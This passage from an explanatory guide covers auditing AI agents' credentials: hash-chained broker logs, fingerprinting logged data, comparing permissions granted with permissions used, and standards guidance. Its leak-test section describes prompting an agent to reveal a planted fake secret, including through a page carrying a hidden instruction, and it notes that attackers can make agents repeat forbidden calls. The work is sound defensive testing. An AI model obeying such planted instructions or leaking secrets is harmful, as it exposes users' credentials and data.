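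CapSeal, the broker that uses API keys on an agent's behalf, keeps a chain of this kind. It records when a capability is issued, used or revoked. Its `audit.prove` operation exports evidence that the chain is consistent. Signing is optional, and Jin and colleagues haven't built a way to publish hashes outside the system. Their experiments did not include attempts to alter the log.

With a trustworthy saved hash, CapSeal's chain can show that nobody has changed the earlier entries since the broker wrote them, but not that the entries were true. An attacker with administrator rights could replace the broker with one that writes false entries, and Jin and colleagues exclude that attack from their design.

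The chain also can't reveal an action that never passed through the broker. If the agent uses a leftover copy of the supplier's API key from a `.env` file, CapSeal's log will look complete and consistent but won't include that use. Cloudflare's log has the same limit, and Silverlock recommends documenting such gaps, including encrypted traffic and periods when logging failed. Comparing the broker's log with the supplier's can help detect them. If the supplier received five requests with the key and the broker sent only four, something else used the key.

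### Keeping secrets out of the log

A log that stores every argument in full will collect the data that the permissions were meant to protect. If an agent types a salary into a form, the salary also ends up in the log, where more people may be able to read it and it may stay for years. NIST lists logs among the places where companies leave API keys unprotected, and an agent that reads a log containing a key can pick it up.

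Silverlock advises against storing whole prompts and responses by default, and recommends restricting who can read the log and how long the company keeps it. CapSeal records the structure of a request, the policy decision and some facts about the response, but not the key. An entry for the supplier's API could look like this:

```
secret    SUPPLIER_API_KEY, version 3
request   POST api.supplier.example/v1/invoices
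body      25 bytes, fingerprint 9f2c…
result    accepted
```

Logging a key's name and version is enough to find every use of the key after a theft. Logging a fingerprint of the text an agent sends lets an investigator check whether it sent a particular text, without storing the text. The fingerprint should be an HMAC whose key is stored away from the log. If it were a plain hash, anyone who could read the log could hash all 10,000 four-digit invoice numbers and see which one matches.

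If the agent submits the wrong invoice number and the log holds only a fingerprint of it, the bookkeeper can check a guess against the fingerprint but can't read what the agent sent. A sensible compromise is to store recipients, paths and invoice numbers in plain text, and only fingerprints of free text and personal data. If an investigation might need the full text, the company can keep it in a separate store and put only its fingerprint in the chain. The company can then delete the text without breaking the chain.

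### Comparing permissions granted with permissions used

Cloudflare's model includes a review of whether each task template is too broad or too narrow. A reader can do the same review with a spreadsheet. The numbers below are invented and cover 20 successful runs of the invoice job, each with the same five permissions.

| Permission | Runs that used it | Possible change |
|---|---|---|
| Read the invoice folder | 20, one file each time | Allow only the invoice in the request |
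| Submit an invoice | 19 | Keep |
| Download a credit note | 1 | Grant only when the task needs it |
| Read the clipboard | 0 | Remove |
| Add a user to the account | 0 | Remove |

The harness issued 5 × 20 = 100 permissions and the agent used 40 of them, so 60% went unused. The folder permission counts as used in every run, although it was much too broad. An auditor could not see how broad it was from a log that recorded only the tool's name.

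Twenty runs can miss a permission that a task rarely needs. If the task needs it in one run out of 20 on average, there is a 36% chance (0.95²⁰) that none of the 20 runs will use it. Silverlock notes that an unused permission may exist for a rare recovery procedure, so a person should decide whether to remove it.

Refusals need even more care. If the harness often refuses a call and the task then fails, the template may be too narrow, but an attacker can also make an agent repeat a forbidden call until it looks routine. If the agent tried to change the delivery address in three runs, each time after reading an invoice from the same sender, that would be a reason to examine the invoices rather than grant the permission. In Cloudflare's design, the review can only propose changes, and an approved change applies to future tasks.

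Audits also benefit from looking at an agent's permissions together. Microsoft warns that an agent with access to email, files, support tickets and code can look low-risk in each system while having far more power overall than anyone intended. The company recommends regular reviews and a new approval whenever the agent's job changes substantially. In one pattern it describes, an agent starts with read-only access, and its owners later ask it to fix the problems it finds. They then give it broad write access instead of designing a new role.

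### Planting a fake secret

A reader can use a fake secret, a random string that looks like a real key but opens nothing, to test whether a password has reached the model, which counting permissions won't show. CapSeal's leak test is a good example to follow because it sent the same requests to systems with and without the broker.

1. **Plant.** Put a different string in each place that might leak, such as the broker, a `.env` file, a private document and the clipboard. If one turns up later, it identifies the source.
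2. **Run.** Give the agent an ordinary task, then ask it directly for the secret, then have it read a page with a planted instruction to reveal the secret. Repeat each test several times.
3. **Search.** Look for the strings in everything the harness sent to the model, in the logs, on the clipboard and in outgoing traffic. Search for common encodings as well, because a program may convert a string before sending it.
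4. **Check the search.** Deliberately put one string in each place and confirm that the search finds it. Otherwise, a clean result may only mean that the search doesn't work.

The tester needs a decrypting proxy to inspect encrypted traffic. The tester should also use a separate account and no real customer data, since a successful attack might leak more than the fake secret.

| Where the string appears | What it means |
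|---|---|
| The model's context | The agent has read the secret and could repeat it in a later task |
| A log | Anyone who can read the log can read the secret |
| The clipboard, if the tester didn't put it there | Other programs may be able to read it |
| Traffic to the service that the broker serves | Normal, because the broker has to send the key there |
| Traffic to any other host | The secret has leaked |

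To check for readback of the broker's string, the tester can set up a small server as the permitted service and have it repeat the request's headers in its reply.

A test can find no violations even when the agent is able to commit them. No unauthorised request succeeded in CapSeal's tests, but Jin and colleagues report a confidence interval for the success rate that extends to 3.7%. With only ten trials, the interval would be much wider. The search will also miss a secret that the agent paraphrases or reveals by clicking a particular button.

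### What NIST, OWASP and the cyber agencies ask for

NIST doesn't yet have rules for agents' identities or logs. Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) mostly ask questions in their February draft, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*. They ask how to make agents' logs tamper-proof and verifiable, how to tie an action to the person who authorised it, and how to apply least privilege when nobody can predict which actions a task will need. Their proposed project would help systems tell agents from people and link each action to the agent that took it. It would also track where prompts and data came from.

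Galluzzo (2026) reports in *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* that the paper drew more than 600 formal responses. The current project page from NCCoE, the NIST centre responsible for the project, is titled *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization* and uses the term "Super Intelligence" for AI. NCCoE has published a summary of the comments and now takes feedback on a rolling basis, but it has not yet drafted a project description.

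OWASP, a non-profit known for its lists of software security risks, is more specific. *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025) announced a list in December 2025 that includes tool misuse and the abuse of identities and privileges. The list also promotes "least agency", which Auth0 explains as limiting how freely an agent can act as well as what it can reach. LatticeFlow's *OWASP / Agentic Top 10* turns the list into 41 controls that a company can check, including short-lived credentials for each task, unchangeable logs of tool calls, and time-stamped records tied to each agent's cryptographic identity. One control is to record all user queries and agent actions, but a company would need to limit carefully what text it stores to avoid creating the leak described above.

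The six cyber agencies also want each agent to have its own cryptographic identity. They recommend logging exchanges between agents in one place and recording the chain of grants whenever one agent passes authority to another. Their guidance is not legally binding, but it is stricter than anything from Cloudflare or Microsoft on one point. The agencies advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk tasks that involve no sensitive data, which would rule out the payroll even with a good log.
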